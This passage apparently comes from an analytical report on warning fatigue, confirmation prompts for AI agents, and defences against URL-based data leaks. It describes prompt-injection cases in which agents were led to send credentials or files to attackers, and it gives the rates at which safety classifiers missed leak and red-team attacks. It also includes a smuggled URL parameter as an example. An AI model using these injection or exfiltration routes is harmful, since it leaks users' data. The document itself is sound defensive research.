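Yan's participants did use this knowledge, stopping about 60% of the unrequested actions and allowing 94.1% of the necessary ones. Suppose, as before, that one constructed URL in 10,000 leaks something, and that users judge links as well as these participants judged actions. Over 10,000 prompts, users would refuse about 590 harmless requests and have a 60% chance of stopping the leak, which is roughly 1,000 harmless requests refused for each leak stopped. A rule that refused every constructed URL would stop every such leak, but it would refuse about ten times as many harmless requests for each one.

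This comparison probably makes the prompt look better than it is. Yan described actions in plain words, while a link dialog may show only a URL. More than a third of the actions in the simulation were also unrequested, so participants had much more reason to stay alert than someone who encounters one leak in 10,000 prompts.

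## Whether repeated prompts stop protecting users

Yan's participants judged 18 prompts in one sitting and stopped most of the unrequested actions. Someone who uses an agent every day may see that many prompts in a week, nearly all about harmless requests. Security researchers have long suspected that people in this position stop reading prompts and approve or dismiss them without weighing them, a problem known as warning fatigue.

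### Three reasons to approve without reading

A user who clicks "open" after half a second may have stopped noticing the dialog, may have decided it isn't worth the time to read, or may just want to get to the page.

People stop noticing warnings because of habituation, a weakening response to a repeated stimulus. Vance, Jenkins and colleagues explain in *Tuning Out Security Warnings* (2018) that people unconsciously compare each new warning with a mental model of earlier ones and pay less attention if it matches. The response partly recovers after a period without warnings.

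Users who don't read a prompt are guessing that it is another false alarm, and that may be reasonable. Cormac Herley, a security researcher at Microsoft, argued in 2009 that people often have sound reasons to reject security advice, because following it burdens them more than the harm it prevents would.

Users may approve even the first prompt they see because they want to finish the task. Someone who asked for train times, for example, won't get them if they refuse the link.

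| Reason for approving | How it develops over time | What should make the user more careful |
|---|---|---|
| Habituation | Grows with each repeat and eases after a break | A dialog that looks different, or longer gaps between prompts |
| A bet on a false alarm | Grows as harmless prompts accumulate, and a break changes little | Fewer false alarms, or more to lose |
| Pressure to finish | Present from the start | Another way to do the task |

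All three can affect the same click. More attention wouldn't help a user who can't interpret the URL.

### How often a prompt matters

Suppose one prompt in 1,000 concerns a link that would leak data, and a user sees 20 prompts a week. On average, the user would then see a prompt for such a link about once every 1,000 ÷ 20 = 50 weeks, after roughly 999 harmless prompts. In a year of 1,040 prompts, the chance of seeing at least one bad link is 1 − 0.999¹⁰⁴⁰, or about 65%.

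Reading every prompt takes time. For example, if careful reading adds five seconds per prompt, about as much as the domain tests by Lain and colleagues did, and one prompt in 1,000 has a bad link, the user spends an extra 5,000 seconds for each bad link they meet. If careful reading stops half of the bad links that a quick click would let through, the user spends 10,000 seconds, or 2.8 hours, for each one they stop.

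| Share of prompts that are bad | Average gap at 20 prompts a week | Chance of at least one in a year | Extra reading time per leak stopped |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 in 100 | 5 weeks | Almost 100% | 17 minutes |
| 1 in 1,000 | 50 weeks | 65% | 2.8 hours |
| 1 in 10,000 | 9.6 years | 10% | 28 hours |

It is sensible to click through confirmation dialogs if you would rather let a spammer have your email address than spend nearly three hours reading them. The same person should read carefully when the conversation contains the key to a customer database. But users can't decide for each link whether to read the dialog, because they have to read the URL to find out what is at stake.

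The bet can also be good for the user but bad for other people, because an employee spends the time reading while the employer or its customers may suffer the leak. At the middle rate in the table, a vendor with a million such users would show them 20,000 bad links a week. If users stopped half, 10,000 leaks a week would still go through.

Users learn little from approving a request that leaks data, because the leak is silent. A user who has approved ten leaks may believe they have never seen one, and may take the prompts for false alarms. Weinberger and Felt argue in *A Week to Remember* that browsers lose users' trust by repeating a warning that users believe is false.

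### Certificate warnings in the laboratory

Much of the research on warning fatigue concerns the warning a browser shows when it can't verify a site's identity from its security certificate. The user then decides whether to continue. Someone may be intercepting the connection, or the site's owner may have let the certificate expire. The browser usually can't tell which, just as an agent's software can't tell whether a link runs a train search or leaks data.

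For *Crying Wolf* (2009), Sunshine, Egelman and colleagues surveyed 409 people about certificate warnings, and fewer than half said they would continue past one. They then tested 100 people in a laboratory, where participants saw a certificate warning when they looked up information on their bank's website and on a university library's. *Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) summarises the laboratory results for three browsers. In Firefox 2, 90% of participants proceeded past the warning on the bank's site and 95% on the library's. The figures were 55% and 60% in Firefox 3, and 90% and 100% in Internet Explorer 7.

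Sunshine and colleagues measured how many people ignored a warning, not whether repetition had made them less careful. Schneier nevertheless introduced their paper, in *Too Many Security Warnings Results in Complacency*, as research that "proves what we already knew". Vance and colleagues note that participants reused their responses to earlier warnings when the risk was different, which Sunshine and colleagues attributed to habituation. That is plausible, but participants who wanted to finish the task would have behaved the same way. Of the 11 earlier studies that Vance and colleagues list, seven inferred habituation without measuring it.

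The laboratory may also have made people careless. When Sotirakopoulos and colleagues repeated the experiment with a more representative group, 80% of Firefox 3.5 users and 72% of Internet Explorer users proceeded to their bank. More than 40% of participants said the setting had influenced them, because they felt safe there or were trying to complete the task. In a study by Schechter and colleagues, 53% of 57 participants proceeded to a banking site, but only 36% of those who used their own passwords did. Akhawe and Felt cite both results as reasons to study warnings outside the laboratory.

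### What 25 million real warnings showed

Akhawe and Felt then did so, using the usage reports that some people agree to send to browser makers. They counted 25,405,944 warnings in Firefox and Chrome in late spring and early summer 2013. For each type of warning, they calculated the click-through rate, the share of warnings that users proceed past.

| Warning | Firefox | Chrome |
|---|---|---|
| Site may install malicious software | 7.2% | 23.2% |
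| Site may be a phishing site | 9.1% | 18.0% |
| Browser can't verify the site's certificate | 33.0% | 70.2% |

People heeded more than three quarters of the malware and phishing warnings in both browsers, but in Chrome they ignored most certificate warnings. These figures don't support a general claim that users ignore warnings.

False alarms may explain much of the difference between warning types. Malware and phishing warnings came from a list that Google maintained, and Akhawe and Felt describe its error rate as negligible. Certificate warnings were much less reliable. An earlier study found that 20% of the thousand most popular sites using encryption triggered a false certificate warning. Akhawe and Felt accept that clicking through such warnings may be "safe and rational", though it may also train people to dismiss real ones.

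The gap between the two browsers is harder to interpret. Firefox saved a user's decision to accept a faulty certificate, while Chrome showed the warning again on every visit. Akhawe and Felt give the example of a user who leaves one faulty site and visits another nine times. Firefox would record one click-through in two warnings, or 50%, while Chrome would record nine in ten, or 90%, for the same behaviour. Chrome also blocked some important sites outright when their certificates failed, which removed the cases in which users were most likely to be careful. Akhawe and Felt estimate that this blocking could account for up to 15 of the 37 percentage points between the browsers. The Firefox figure is also less reliable because it comes from about 11,000 warnings shown to people testing pre-release versions, compared with 16.7 million warnings for Chrome.

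Akhawe and Felt also found a pattern that fits warning fatigue. The most common certificate error in Chrome, an unknown issuer, made up 56.0% of the total, and users proceeded past 81.8% of these warnings. Expired certificates made up 17.6%, and users proceeded past 57.4% of those warnings. Users clicked through about half of the unknown-issuer warnings within 1.7 seconds, compared with 2.7 seconds for expired certificates.

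Either habituation or learning would produce this pattern. A site with an unknown issuer triggers the warning on every visit, so regular visitors have good reason to expect it, whereas they wouldn't expect a certificate that has just expired. Akhawe and Felt cite the gap in click-through rates both as a sign of fatigue and as a sign that some users notice what a warning is about. The gap could reflect both, but it doesn't show which matters more.

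### Experiments that measured habituation

Users may dismiss a warning because they have stopped noticing it (habituation) or because they reasonably expect a false alarm. A researcher can tell these apart by changing only the warning's appearance and keeping the risk constant. A new colour or layout might regain the attention of users who had stopped noticing the warning, but it shouldn't change how likely users think a false alarm is.

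*How Polymorphic Warnings Reduce Habituation in the Brain* (Anderson, Kirwan and colleagues, 2015) reports brain scans of people viewing the same warning repeatedly. Activity in the brain's visual processing centres dropped sharply after the second exposure and kept declining with further exposures. The decline was slower for "polymorphic" warnings, which change their appearance each time.

Vance and colleagues extended this to a five-day working week, scanning 15 people and tracking their eyes each day as they looked at images of warnings and ordinary software. Participants' eyes rested on an average of 9.1 points per viewing on the first day and 7.35 on the fifth. Their attention only partly recovered overnight. Participants only rated how serious each warning was, so the experiment couldn't show whether they would have ignored it.

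A second experiment by the same researchers did measure decisions, over three weeks. They asked students to install and rank three apps each weekday from an app store that the students believed was unrelated to the study. Before each installation, the store listed the permissions the app wanted. Four permissions were forbidden, including charging purchases to the user's credit card and deleting their photos. Participants had to pass a quiz on these before starting, so they knew what to refuse.

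The 102 people who took part for at least half the days saw 7,248 permission warnings, about five per person per weekday. More than a third of the warnings contained a forbidden permission. The store showed 55 participants the same warning design every time, and they refused 87% of the risky apps at the start but only 55% after three weeks. The other 47 saw a design that kept changing, and their refusal rate fell from 87% to 76%.

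This is strong evidence that habituation affects behaviour. The researchers assigned the designs at random, and both groups faced the same risks and had to find three apps, so neither a reasonable bet on those risks nor pressure to finish can easily explain why one group ended 21 points lower. The cause of the remaining 11-point fall, which also occurred with the changing design, is less clear. Those participants may have become habituated to the changing warnings too, or may have noticed that nothing bad happened when they installed a risky app.

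In the statistical model, each further warning lowered the odds of a refusal by about 2.7% with the fixed design and 1.2% with the changing one, which suggests a gradual decline. A break of a day or more roughly doubled the odds of a refusal, although this estimate is imprecise.

The participants were students with an average age of 22, and 32 of the original 134 dropped out too early to be included. But unlike Sunshine's participants, they used their own phones in their own time, and they saw about as many warnings a day as a regular user of a browsing agent might.

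Vance and colleagues also summarise two online experiments by Bravo-Lillo and colleagues. In one, people saw a dialog many times in quick succession before its text changed, and only 14% noticed the change immediately. In the other, showing the dialog more often cut the share who noticed to a third. A link prompt has the same weakness, since only the URL changes while the title, warning and buttons stay the same.

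### Warnings that kept working

The malware and phishing warnings in Akhawe and Felt's study are the best evidence that a warning can protect people in everyday use. Nearly all of these warnings were correct, so the share of users who turned back is close to the share of real threats stopped. Firefox's malware warning stopped about 93% of attempted visits, and Chrome's stopped about 77%.

The click-through rate for Chrome's warnings varied from week to week, between 11.2% and 24.9%. Akhawe and Felt suspect that this happened when a well-known site accidentally loaded an advertisement from a listed domain. Chrome then blocked the whole page with a warning, and users who trusted the site may not have believed the warning. Firefox blocked only the advertisement, without a warning, and its rate stayed steady.

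Google later showed it could improve even the certificate warning that most Chrome users ignored. In *Improving SSL Warnings* (2015), Felt, Ainslie and colleagues replaced the technical text with a short message saying that attackers might be trying to steal the user's information. They also made the button for leaving the page bright blue and hid the link for continuing behind the word "Advanced". They then showed different versions to users of pre-release Chrome, with more than 4,000 warnings per version.

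Users turned back from 30.9% of the old warnings and 58.3% of the new ones. When the new text appeared in the old design, they turned back from 32.1%, so nearly all of the gain came from the buttons and layout. When Google released the new version to everyone in August 2014, the share of warnings that users heeded rose from 37% to 62%. Several months and tens of millions of warnings later, it was still 61%.

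A gain that came only from novelty should have faded in that time. It may have lasted because the warning was rare. Most Chrome users saw at most one certificate warning a month, while the students in Vance's experiment saw about five permission warnings a day and became less careful within three weeks.

The new design persuaded people to turn back but didn't help them much to understand why. On a survey question with two possible answers, 49.2% of people shown the new text correctly said that a hacker might read their email, compared with 37.7% of those shown the old text. Guessing would produce about 50%. Felt and colleagues also couldn't tell which warnings concerned real attacks, so people may have become better at avoiding attacks, or just more likely to leave harmless sites too.

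This difference matters for links because the prompt is there to let tasks like train searches go ahead. If a vendor copied the design by making "don't open" a large blue button, users would probably refuse more leaks, but they would also refuse more train searches.

By 2018, habituation no longer looked like the main problem with browser warnings. *An Experience Sampling Study of User Reactions to Browser Warnings* (2018), by Malkin and Egelman with colleagues at Google, surveyed more than 6,000 Chrome and Firefox users as they encountered real warnings. According to *Adrienne Porter Felt*, a Google Research page about one of those colleagues, people's reasons varied with the situation, and no single failure, such as habituation, prevented good decisions. The survey may have missed some habituation, because people can't easily report a process they are unaware of. But it suggests that many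 people had a reason for proceeding, even if it was mistaken.

### What approval rates for coding agents can show

AI agents ask for approval far more often than browsers show warnings. In Claude Code's manual mode, a developer may have to approve shell commands, file changes and page fetches throughout the day. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* (March 2026) reported that users accepted 93% of these prompts. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) put the share at 97% and concluded that many users were approving prompts by reflex.

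A high approval rate doesn't prove that repeated prompts stop protecting users, though that may be true. Suppose one request in 1,000 is dangerous. A user who rejects only the dangerous requests would approve 99.9% of prompts, and a user who never reads them would approve 100%, so the rates are almost the same even though only the first user catches anything dangerous. A 97% approval rate could come from someone who reads every prompt and turns down 3% of requests because they would prefer a different approach.

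Anthropic also points out that users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, so they don't approve everything they are shown. But a plan leaves more room for disagreement than a command. A developer may reject a plan because it uses the wrong library, then approve every command in the revised plan because they have already agreed to that plan.

The rise from 93% to 97% is also an unclear sign of growing fatigue. Anthropic doesn't explain in either post how it counted, and a newer model might make fewer requests worth refusing.

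Another measure is how often people stop reviewing actions one at a time. In February 2026 Anthropic published a study of how people's use of Claude Code changes with experience. According to jc-aiwiki, a third-party summary, new users let Claude run without manual approval in about 20% of sessions, and users with 750 or more sessions did so in over 40%. Anthropic's text, reproduced in The Greek Courier's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026), includes the caution that manual approval is the default, so some of the rise may come from people who always wanted the agent to have more independence and only later changed the setting.

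The same users also interrupted Claude more often. According to the summary, experienced users interrupted in 9% of turns, compared with about 5% for people with around ten sessions. Digital Watch's *AI agent autonomy rises as users gain trust in Anthropic's Claude Code* adds that experienced users interrupt more when something seems unusual. If they had stopped paying attention, they would probably have interrupted less. They may have moved from checking each step to watching the work as a whole. That can be a sensible use of limited attention, but it works less well for a leak, because an interruption after the request has gone out comes too late.

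Many users have also turned prompts off. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule that let some shell commands run without a prompt. Anthropic says most of these rules were very broad. For example, a rule that allows any Python program allows almost anything a program can do. A quarter of interactive sessions started in a mode that skips permission checks.

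Users who write a rule or choose a mode that skips prompts seem to have decided that the prompts aren't worth the interruption. Habituation alone doesn't explain this, since it takes a deliberate step. Skipping prompts can be less secure than clicking through them, because even an inattentive user might notice a strange request on the screen.

### Planting a dangerous command

Researchers can better detect fatigue by planting a bad request among harmless ones and seeing who refuses it. They know this request should be refused, so the result doesn't depend on how many of the others deserved approval.

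Anthropic ran such a test before it made auto mode the default. Auto mode replaces most prompts with an automated check. Anthropic hired 1,053 testers through a research vendor, and they knew only that they were taking part in a coding study. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The software did not run that command, even if the tester approved it.

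Only 143 of the 1,053 testers (13.6%) refused the commands. The commands could be recognised, since auto mode's automated check blocked 89% of them. Testers caught about 17% early in a session, but about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

The drop is consistent with warning fatigue, but even early in the session, testers let through about 83% of the dangerous commands. Repetition within the session therefore can't be the main cause of the failure. Testers may have brought a habit of approving prompts from their ordinary work, been concentrating on the coding task, or assumed that nothing in a test environment could do real harm.

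Late in the session, the testers refused 5% of dangerous commands. Claude Code's real users refuse 3% of all prompts, and presumably nearly all the prompts they see are harmless. If the testers refused harmless prompts at about the same rate, they could hardly tell dangerous commands from harmless ones by then. Anthropic doesn't report how many harmless prompts the testers refused, so this is a rough comparison between two different groups.

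The early and late figures also come from different people, because each tester saw only one planted command. Anthropic doesn't say whether it chose at random when each tester saw the command, or how many saw it late. If people who approve without reading get through prompts faster, they are more likely to reach the fiftieth prompt. Some of the drop could then reflect who was still being tested rather than testers becoming less attentive.

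Developers working on their own projects might catch more than 13.6%, because Anthropic's testers had no code of their own to lose. In the laboratory studies of certificate warnings, people took risks because they felt safe or wanted to finish, and the testers may have done the same. But the testers also knew that someone was evaluating them, which may have made them more careful than usual. Anthropic published the result to support a change in its product, and it hasn't released the underlying data with the post.

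Yan's participants did much better, stopping about 60% of the unrequested actions, but their prompts were in plain language, and participants should have refused more than a third of them. Anthropic's testers saw one dangerous command in a session that could include more than 50 harmless ones, which is closer to how a user would encounter a link that leaks data.

If users caught only 13.6% of bad links, a person who saw one every 50 weeks would catch about one every seven years and let roughly six through in that time.

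### How much of this applies to link prompts

None of these studies tested an AI agent's link prompts. The closest study, by Lain and colleagues, used emails in a single session and didn't follow people over weeks of prompts. OpenAI gives no measurements for its dialog.

How soon people stop reading link prompts probably depends most on how many they see. A person who asks ChatGPT occasional questions might see an unverified link once a month, about as often as most Chrome users saw a certificate warning. Felt's results suggest that a well-designed dialog could keep that person's attention for a long time. By the earlier calculation, someone who runs a 40-page research task every working day could get 30 prompts a week, slightly more than the students in Vance's experiment saw. Among the students whose warnings always looked the same, refusals of risky apps fell by 32 points in three weeks.

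People who see many link prompts also have less reason to stay alert than those students did. More than a third of the students' warnings contained a permission they knew they had to refuse. Almost every link prompt may be a false alarm, and a request that leaks data often looks like an ordinary search.

In some ways, users may find links easier to refuse than commands or browser warnings. The agent can often find another source, and a warning that a link may share conversation data gives users a clearer reason to stop than a routine request to run a command.

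The finding that repetition weakens attention is the most likely to apply to confirmation prompts for AI agents, since it has appeared in brain scans, eye movements and decisions about apps. The percentages are much less likely to apply. How often developers miss a destructive command is not a measure of how often travellers would approve a hotel link that leaks data.

A vendor could measure that rate directly by adapting Anthropic's method. In a product study with consenting users, the software would replace one harmless link, at a randomly chosen point, with a URL containing an invented private detail, and would send nothing whichever button the user clicked. The vendor would also need to record refusals of harmless links, because otherwise someone who refuses everything would appear to be a perfect reviewer.

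To find out why people approve bad links, the vendor could vary one condition at a time. If a new prompt layout reduces these approvals, habituation is probably part of the problem. If people read more carefully when the conversation contains something valuable, they are probably weighing the risk. If offering another source leads to more refusals, people were probably approving links to get the task done.

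If the true catch rates were 17% early and 5% late, as in Anthropic's test, such a study would need only about 100 people in each group for an 80% chance of detecting the difference at the usual 5% significance level. Each person should see only one planted link, because someone who has just caught a leak will read the next dialog more carefully than an ordinary user would.

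## Ways to ask less often without reopening the leak

A vendor can cut confirmation prompts by allowing more requests without asking, but some of those requests will leak data. Several designs try to prevent this by limiting what the agent can put in a request or what data it has when it makes one. Another has a second model decide, in place of the user, whether to allow a request.

### URL templates with restricted slots

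A URL template is an address with gaps, or slots, for particular values. The model chooses the values, and ordinary software checks them and writes the address. For the imaginary hotel site with 1,000 cities, the template could be:

`hotels.example/search?city={city}&arrive={date}&nights={nights}&guests={guests}`

Suppose a user wants a room in York for two people, for two nights from 6 November 2026.

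1. The model picks the hotel template and supplies "York", "2026-11-06", "2" and "2".
2. The software checks that York is on the site's list of cities, that the date falls within the next 365 days, that the stay is 1 to 14 nights and that the party has one to four people.
3. If every value passes, the software fills in the template and sends the request without a prompt. If the model has put `York&email=anna@mail.example` in the city slot, the check fails, because no city has that name.

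A domain allowlist would have let that email address through. With a template, the model can't add a parameter or change the path.

The slots can still carry up to 24.3 bits per search, as calculated earlier for this site. Leaking a 128-bit access key would take six searches, and an agent comparing prices for 40 dates could send up to 971 bits. Only the site would receive this data, as with a narrow connector, so the risk depends on who can register a template. If anyone can, an attacker will register their own "hotel search", but if the vendor has to approve each template, small sites will probably have to wait for approval.

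Allowing free text in a template removes most of the protection, as it does in connectors. Templates therefore suit hotels, trains and weather APIs better than a pharmacy, where the user needs to search for terms like "glucose test strips". They also don't help an agent follow links, except on sites where a page number can be a slot.

There don't seem to be any published tests of URL templates in a web agent. The closest work is *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025), which labels data by how much information it can carry. A yes/no answer ranks below a choice from a list, which ranks below free text. The paper's software could let a yes/no answer extracted from an untrusted page influence an action, because the page contributes at most one bit. The paper's tests left this feature out because most of the tasks didn't need it.

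### Tracking where each value came from

A URL containing "London" doesn't show whether the user typed the city for this task or the agent remembered it from an old chat. Software can track this by labelling each piece of data with its source when the agent first receives it and keeping the label attached as the data moves. A vendor could then apply a rule such as "a value the user typed for this task may go to the site the user named".

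CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), combines such labels with two language models. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which builds on it, explains how the models divide the work. One receives the user's request and writes a plan as a short program. The other extracts information from sources such as web pages and emails, but has no tools. Separate software runs the program, calls the tools and stores the extracted information in labelled variables. A hostile page can change a value, such as a hotel's price, but can't add a step to the program. According to *SPA* (2026), the labels record where a value came from and who may receive it, and the software checks them against each tool's rules.

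Using two models without the labels isn't enough to prevent leaks. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) gives an example in which an injected instruction gets the second model to quote private notes in a reply. The plan already includes sending that reply, so the notes leak without any extra step.

FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, plans one step at a time. When a tool returns untrusted text, the software hides it behind a variable name. The planning model can pass the variable to another tool without reading the text. It can also open the variable, but the software then treats its later decisions as untrusted and blocks actions that require a trusted decision. The labels on data become stricter when the data is combined. If Anna, Ben and Carl may read one document, and Ben, Carl and Dina another, only Ben and Carl may read a summary of both.

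With this kind of tracking, a user could type "find a room in York from 6 November on hotels.example" and get results without a confirmation prompt, because the user supplied both values and named the site. Tracking can also distinguish the two requests for `cars.example/car_search/London` described earlier, which have the same URL but different labels.

The software would still have to ask about some reasonable requests. "Find the cheapest cover" doesn't name an insurer, and "book somewhere near my sister" relies on an address from the user's contacts. The user has arguably authorised both, but neither counts as authorised under the rule. The number of prompts would depend partly on how precisely people word their requests.

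Tracking could also let agents follow some links again. If the plan is to open the next page of a list, the software can take the link from the page without showing the page to the planning model. The choice doesn't depend on private data, so it reveals little. Choosing the most useful of 26 links is harder, because a model has to read them first.

FIDES tracks data copied into a request, but Costa and colleagues acknowledge that someone who sees which tools the agent calls, and in what order, may still infer limited information. They consider a complete fix too restrictive, because an agent that had read anything private could hardly contact a public site afterwards. CaMeL has a strict mode that also labels values affected by an earlier decision. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* says this mode is meant to close the leak but doesn't test whether it does.

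Costa and colleagues list rules for their experiment that cover posting to a web page and downloading a file, but not opening a page. A vendor would have to add a rule for opening pages to stop an attack like Paul's, in which Claude spelled out a name by opening links.

Someone also has to supply the labels. The software can often use an email's sender and recipients to work out who may read it, but private details also turn up reworded in other text. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) registers private records with their owners and permitted recipients, then has a language model check whether an outgoing message draws on them. This can catch a paraphrase that a search for exact words would miss, but part of the protection then depends on a model's judgement again.

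### Tasks completed and prompts avoided

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 simulated user tasks and 36 attack goals. With GPT-4o and no rules enforced, they counted 152 successful attacks on a basic agent and 21 on FIDES. With the rules enforced, they counted none on either. AgentDojo's automatic scoring recorded three successful attacks on FIDES, but the researchers judged that these weren't real. In some such cases the software had blocked the action.

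The rules also stopped many legitimate tasks. The table shows the share of tasks completed when there was no attack.

| Environment | Basic agent, no rules | Basic agent with rules | FIDES with rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack messages | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

Across the four environments, FIDES completed an average of about 50% of tasks, compared with 84% for the unprotected agent. It did worst in travel, the environment most like a hotel search, partly because GPT-4o struggled to use the variables. With o1, a stronger model at the time, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks, so it might reduce completion rates less with current models.

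A better model wouldn't solve every problem. Many of the blocked banking tasks required the agent to follow instructions in a file, and prompt injections also rely on the agent following instructions in what it reads. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) calls this a fundamental limitation of separating planning from untrusted data. An agent that has to follow a website's directions to find a form could have the same problem.

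Later papers describe CaMeL's results on the same benchmark in general terms. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) reports that CaMeL was much more secure than three simpler defences, at a "comparatively modest utility cost". *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) puts the loss in task completion for designs of this type at up to 30%.

Kolluri and colleagues, who include several of the FIDES researchers, also argue that such comparisons are unfair because the protected agent has to finish without human help, whereas a real unprotected agent would keep stopping for approval. They therefore counted how many approvals each agent would need on the tasks it completed. With the o3-mini model, a basic agent that asked before every consequential action needed 48.2 approvals across the benchmark, the same agent with labels and rules needed 32.4, and FIDES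 needed 18.8.

Their own agent, PRUDENTIA, also tells the planning model the rules, so the model can avoid steps that would need approval. With o4-mini, PRUDENTIA needed 19.2 approvals, compared with 36.8 for FIDES, but completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2% against 75.7%).

PRUDENTIA avoids some prompts by asking the user to vouch for a whole document. If an email contains a to-do list with ten items, the user can approve the email once instead of approving ten actions. But a user who vouches for a hostile email has approved every instruction in it. The researchers counted the prompts an agent would have shown and assumed that users would approve them. The results show that people would see fewer prompts, but no users took part, so the study didn't test whether they would judge them better.

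Kolluri and colleagues also tried PRUDENTIA in a browser, on simulated GitLab and Reddit sites. They allowed it to click, type or open an address only if its decision didn't depend on untrusted text. PRUDENTIA blocked every attack and needed no approvals, while the basic agent needed an average of between 1.0 and 3.65 per task. But the only user tasks were posting a comment and upvoting a post, and the agent could do both without reading anything untrusted. To compare hotels, an agent has to read untrusted text on the hotels' pages.

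### Browsing without private data

An agent can't leak information it doesn't have. An assistant that knows the user's emails and past chats could start a separate browsing session with no memory, files or logins, and give it a brief such as "double room in York, two nights from 6 November". The session could follow any link and compose any URL, return the prices and close.

This would restore all three kinds of task on public sites without a confirmation prompt. At worst, a hostile page could leak the user data in the brief, most of which a hotel site would receive anyway.

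Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* makes the same argument about access keys, which can't leak from a sandbox they never enter. It describes a security exercise in February 2026 in which a researcher tricked an Anthropic employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that looked like routine set-up instructions. One of the steps was to send the employee's cloud credentials to an outside server, and Claude did this in 24 of 25 runs. A check based on what the user asked for would not have stopped this, because the instruction came from the user. Keeping the credentials out of the session would have prevented the leak.

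The weak points are the brief and the results. The main assistant writes the brief, and it could include the user's divorce or income, much as the shopping agents studied by Roh and colleagues did. A form with fixed fields would limit this. The results can contain a hidden instruction. Anthropic warns that a main agent may trust a report from one of its own helpers more than it would trust a web page, which gives attackers a new way to manipulate it. If the main assistant can also open URLs, the instruction could get it to leak the private data. It would be safer for the browsing session to return only certain facts, such as a hotel's name and price.

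A session without logins can't read the user's orders or use an API that needs a private key. It also lacks personal details, such as the user's need for a step-free room, unless the brief includes them. Some tasks need private data, such as a date of birth for an insurance quote. The session could hold only that date and the postcode, so a leak would expose nothing else.

No one seems to have published measurements of this design either. The nearest evidence is from Roh and colleagues, whose agents completed more tasks after the researchers removed irrelevant personal details.

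### Sandboxes with network limits

Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes a sandbox for the shell commands Claude Code runs. The operating system stops these commands from changing files outside the project folder. Their network traffic must pass through a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that checks each domain against a list and prompts the user about new ones. The same limits apply to any program a command starts.

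Anthropic says the sandbox needs to limit both network access and which files the agent can change. With open network access, a hijacked agent could send out the user's files. If it could change any file, it could escape the sandbox and regain network access.

In Anthropic's internal use, sandboxing reduced permission prompts by 84%. Anthropic doesn't say how many people or sessions this covers, or which prompts disappeared. Many were probably requests to run commands, since the sandbox still asks about new domains. The figure therefore can't be applied directly to prompts about links.

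A sandbox works well for repeated searches and API calls on a few known hosts, where a command can go through a long list without interruption. It helps less with links to many different sites, because each new domain triggers another prompt.

Data can also leak through an approved host, as it did when Claude Cowork uploaded a user's files to an attacker's Anthropic account. Anthropic concluded that approving a domain means approving everything the site can do, including accepting uploads. It added a proxy that inspects requests to its own API and passes only those carrying the session's own token, so an attacker's key no longer works.

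A proxy like this could also enforce URL templates, for example by allowing only hotel searches on `hotels.example`. Users of Anthropic's Claude Code sandbox can add their own rules to its proxy. To enforce a template, the proxy would have to decrypt the traffic, because otherwise only the host is visible.

### Letting a classifier approve routine requests

In Claude Code's auto mode, a classifier, which is a second model, decides whether each action may go ahead. In a post dated 7 August 2026, Anthropic confirmed press reports that auto mode would become the default in mid-August. It became the default on 14 August for new Claude Code sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans, except for people who had already chosen another default. Anthropic added on 22 October that most Claude apps on those plans would get the same default the following week.

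Anthropic says that in March, the system let Claude read files and edit the current project without a check, but sent web fetches and most shell commands to the classifier. The classifier received the user's messages and Claude's proposed actions, but not web pages or Claude's own explanations, so neither could lead it to a bad decision. A quick first pass gave a yes or no, leaning towards blocking, and a slower second pass reconsidered anything the first had flagged.

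When the classifier blocks an action, Claude looks for another way to do the task. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, the user has to step in.

The classifier would probably approve the York hotel search, because the user asked for a room in York and the URL searches for one. It would probably block a request that sent Anna's email address to `attacker.example`, since nothing in her messages called for it. But it can't tell whether Claude copied a URL from a page or made it up, because it doesn't see the page. A museum link that secretly reveals the answer to a question about the user would look as harmless to the classifier as it does to a person.

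Anthropic published these error rates in March:

| Error | First pass alone | Both passes |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless actions blocked (10,000 real actions by Anthropic staff's agents) | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Actions beyond what the user had authorised, but allowed (52 real cases) | 6.6% | 17% |
| Invented attempts to leak data, but allowed (1,000 cases) | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second pass removes most of the false alarms, but about three times as many leaks get through. The leak attempts included access keys placed in URLs, so the last row is the most relevant to URL exfiltration. The 17% comes from only 52 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%.

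Suppose that these rates also applied to constructed URLs and that, as before, one in 10,000 leaks something. Over 10,000 requests, the classifier would block about 40 harmless ones and have a 94% chance of stopping the leak. It would therefore block about 42 harmless requests for each leak it stopped, compared with roughly 1,000 for users who judge as well as Yan's participants. The real figure could be much worse, because Anthropic measured false alarms on its own staff's coding work, not on travel or medical searches.

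Anthropic strengthened the classifier after Apollo Research, an AI safety organisation, attacked it with synthetic examples. The share of attacks it missed fell from 12% to 7%. Some of those attacks came from a set that Anthropic never saw, and the new version caught about half of the attacks in that set that the old version had missed.

In another test that Anthropic commissioned, Trajectory Labs ran 720 prompt injection attempts against each of three Claude models in auto mode, and none succeeded. This is little evidence of how well the classifier works, because only 0.09% of attempts succeeded on average against Anthropic's latest models without the classifier, and Trajectory Labs had developed the attacks against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7.

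### Whether a classifier should replace the prompt

The main argument for classifiers is that their performance doesn't decline over a long session. In Anthropic's experiment with planted commands, testers caught fewer dangerous commands after many prompts, while auto mode's catch rate didn't change with session length. Classifiers also reduce the number of prompts, so users may read the remaining ones more carefully, though Anthropic hasn't reported testing this.

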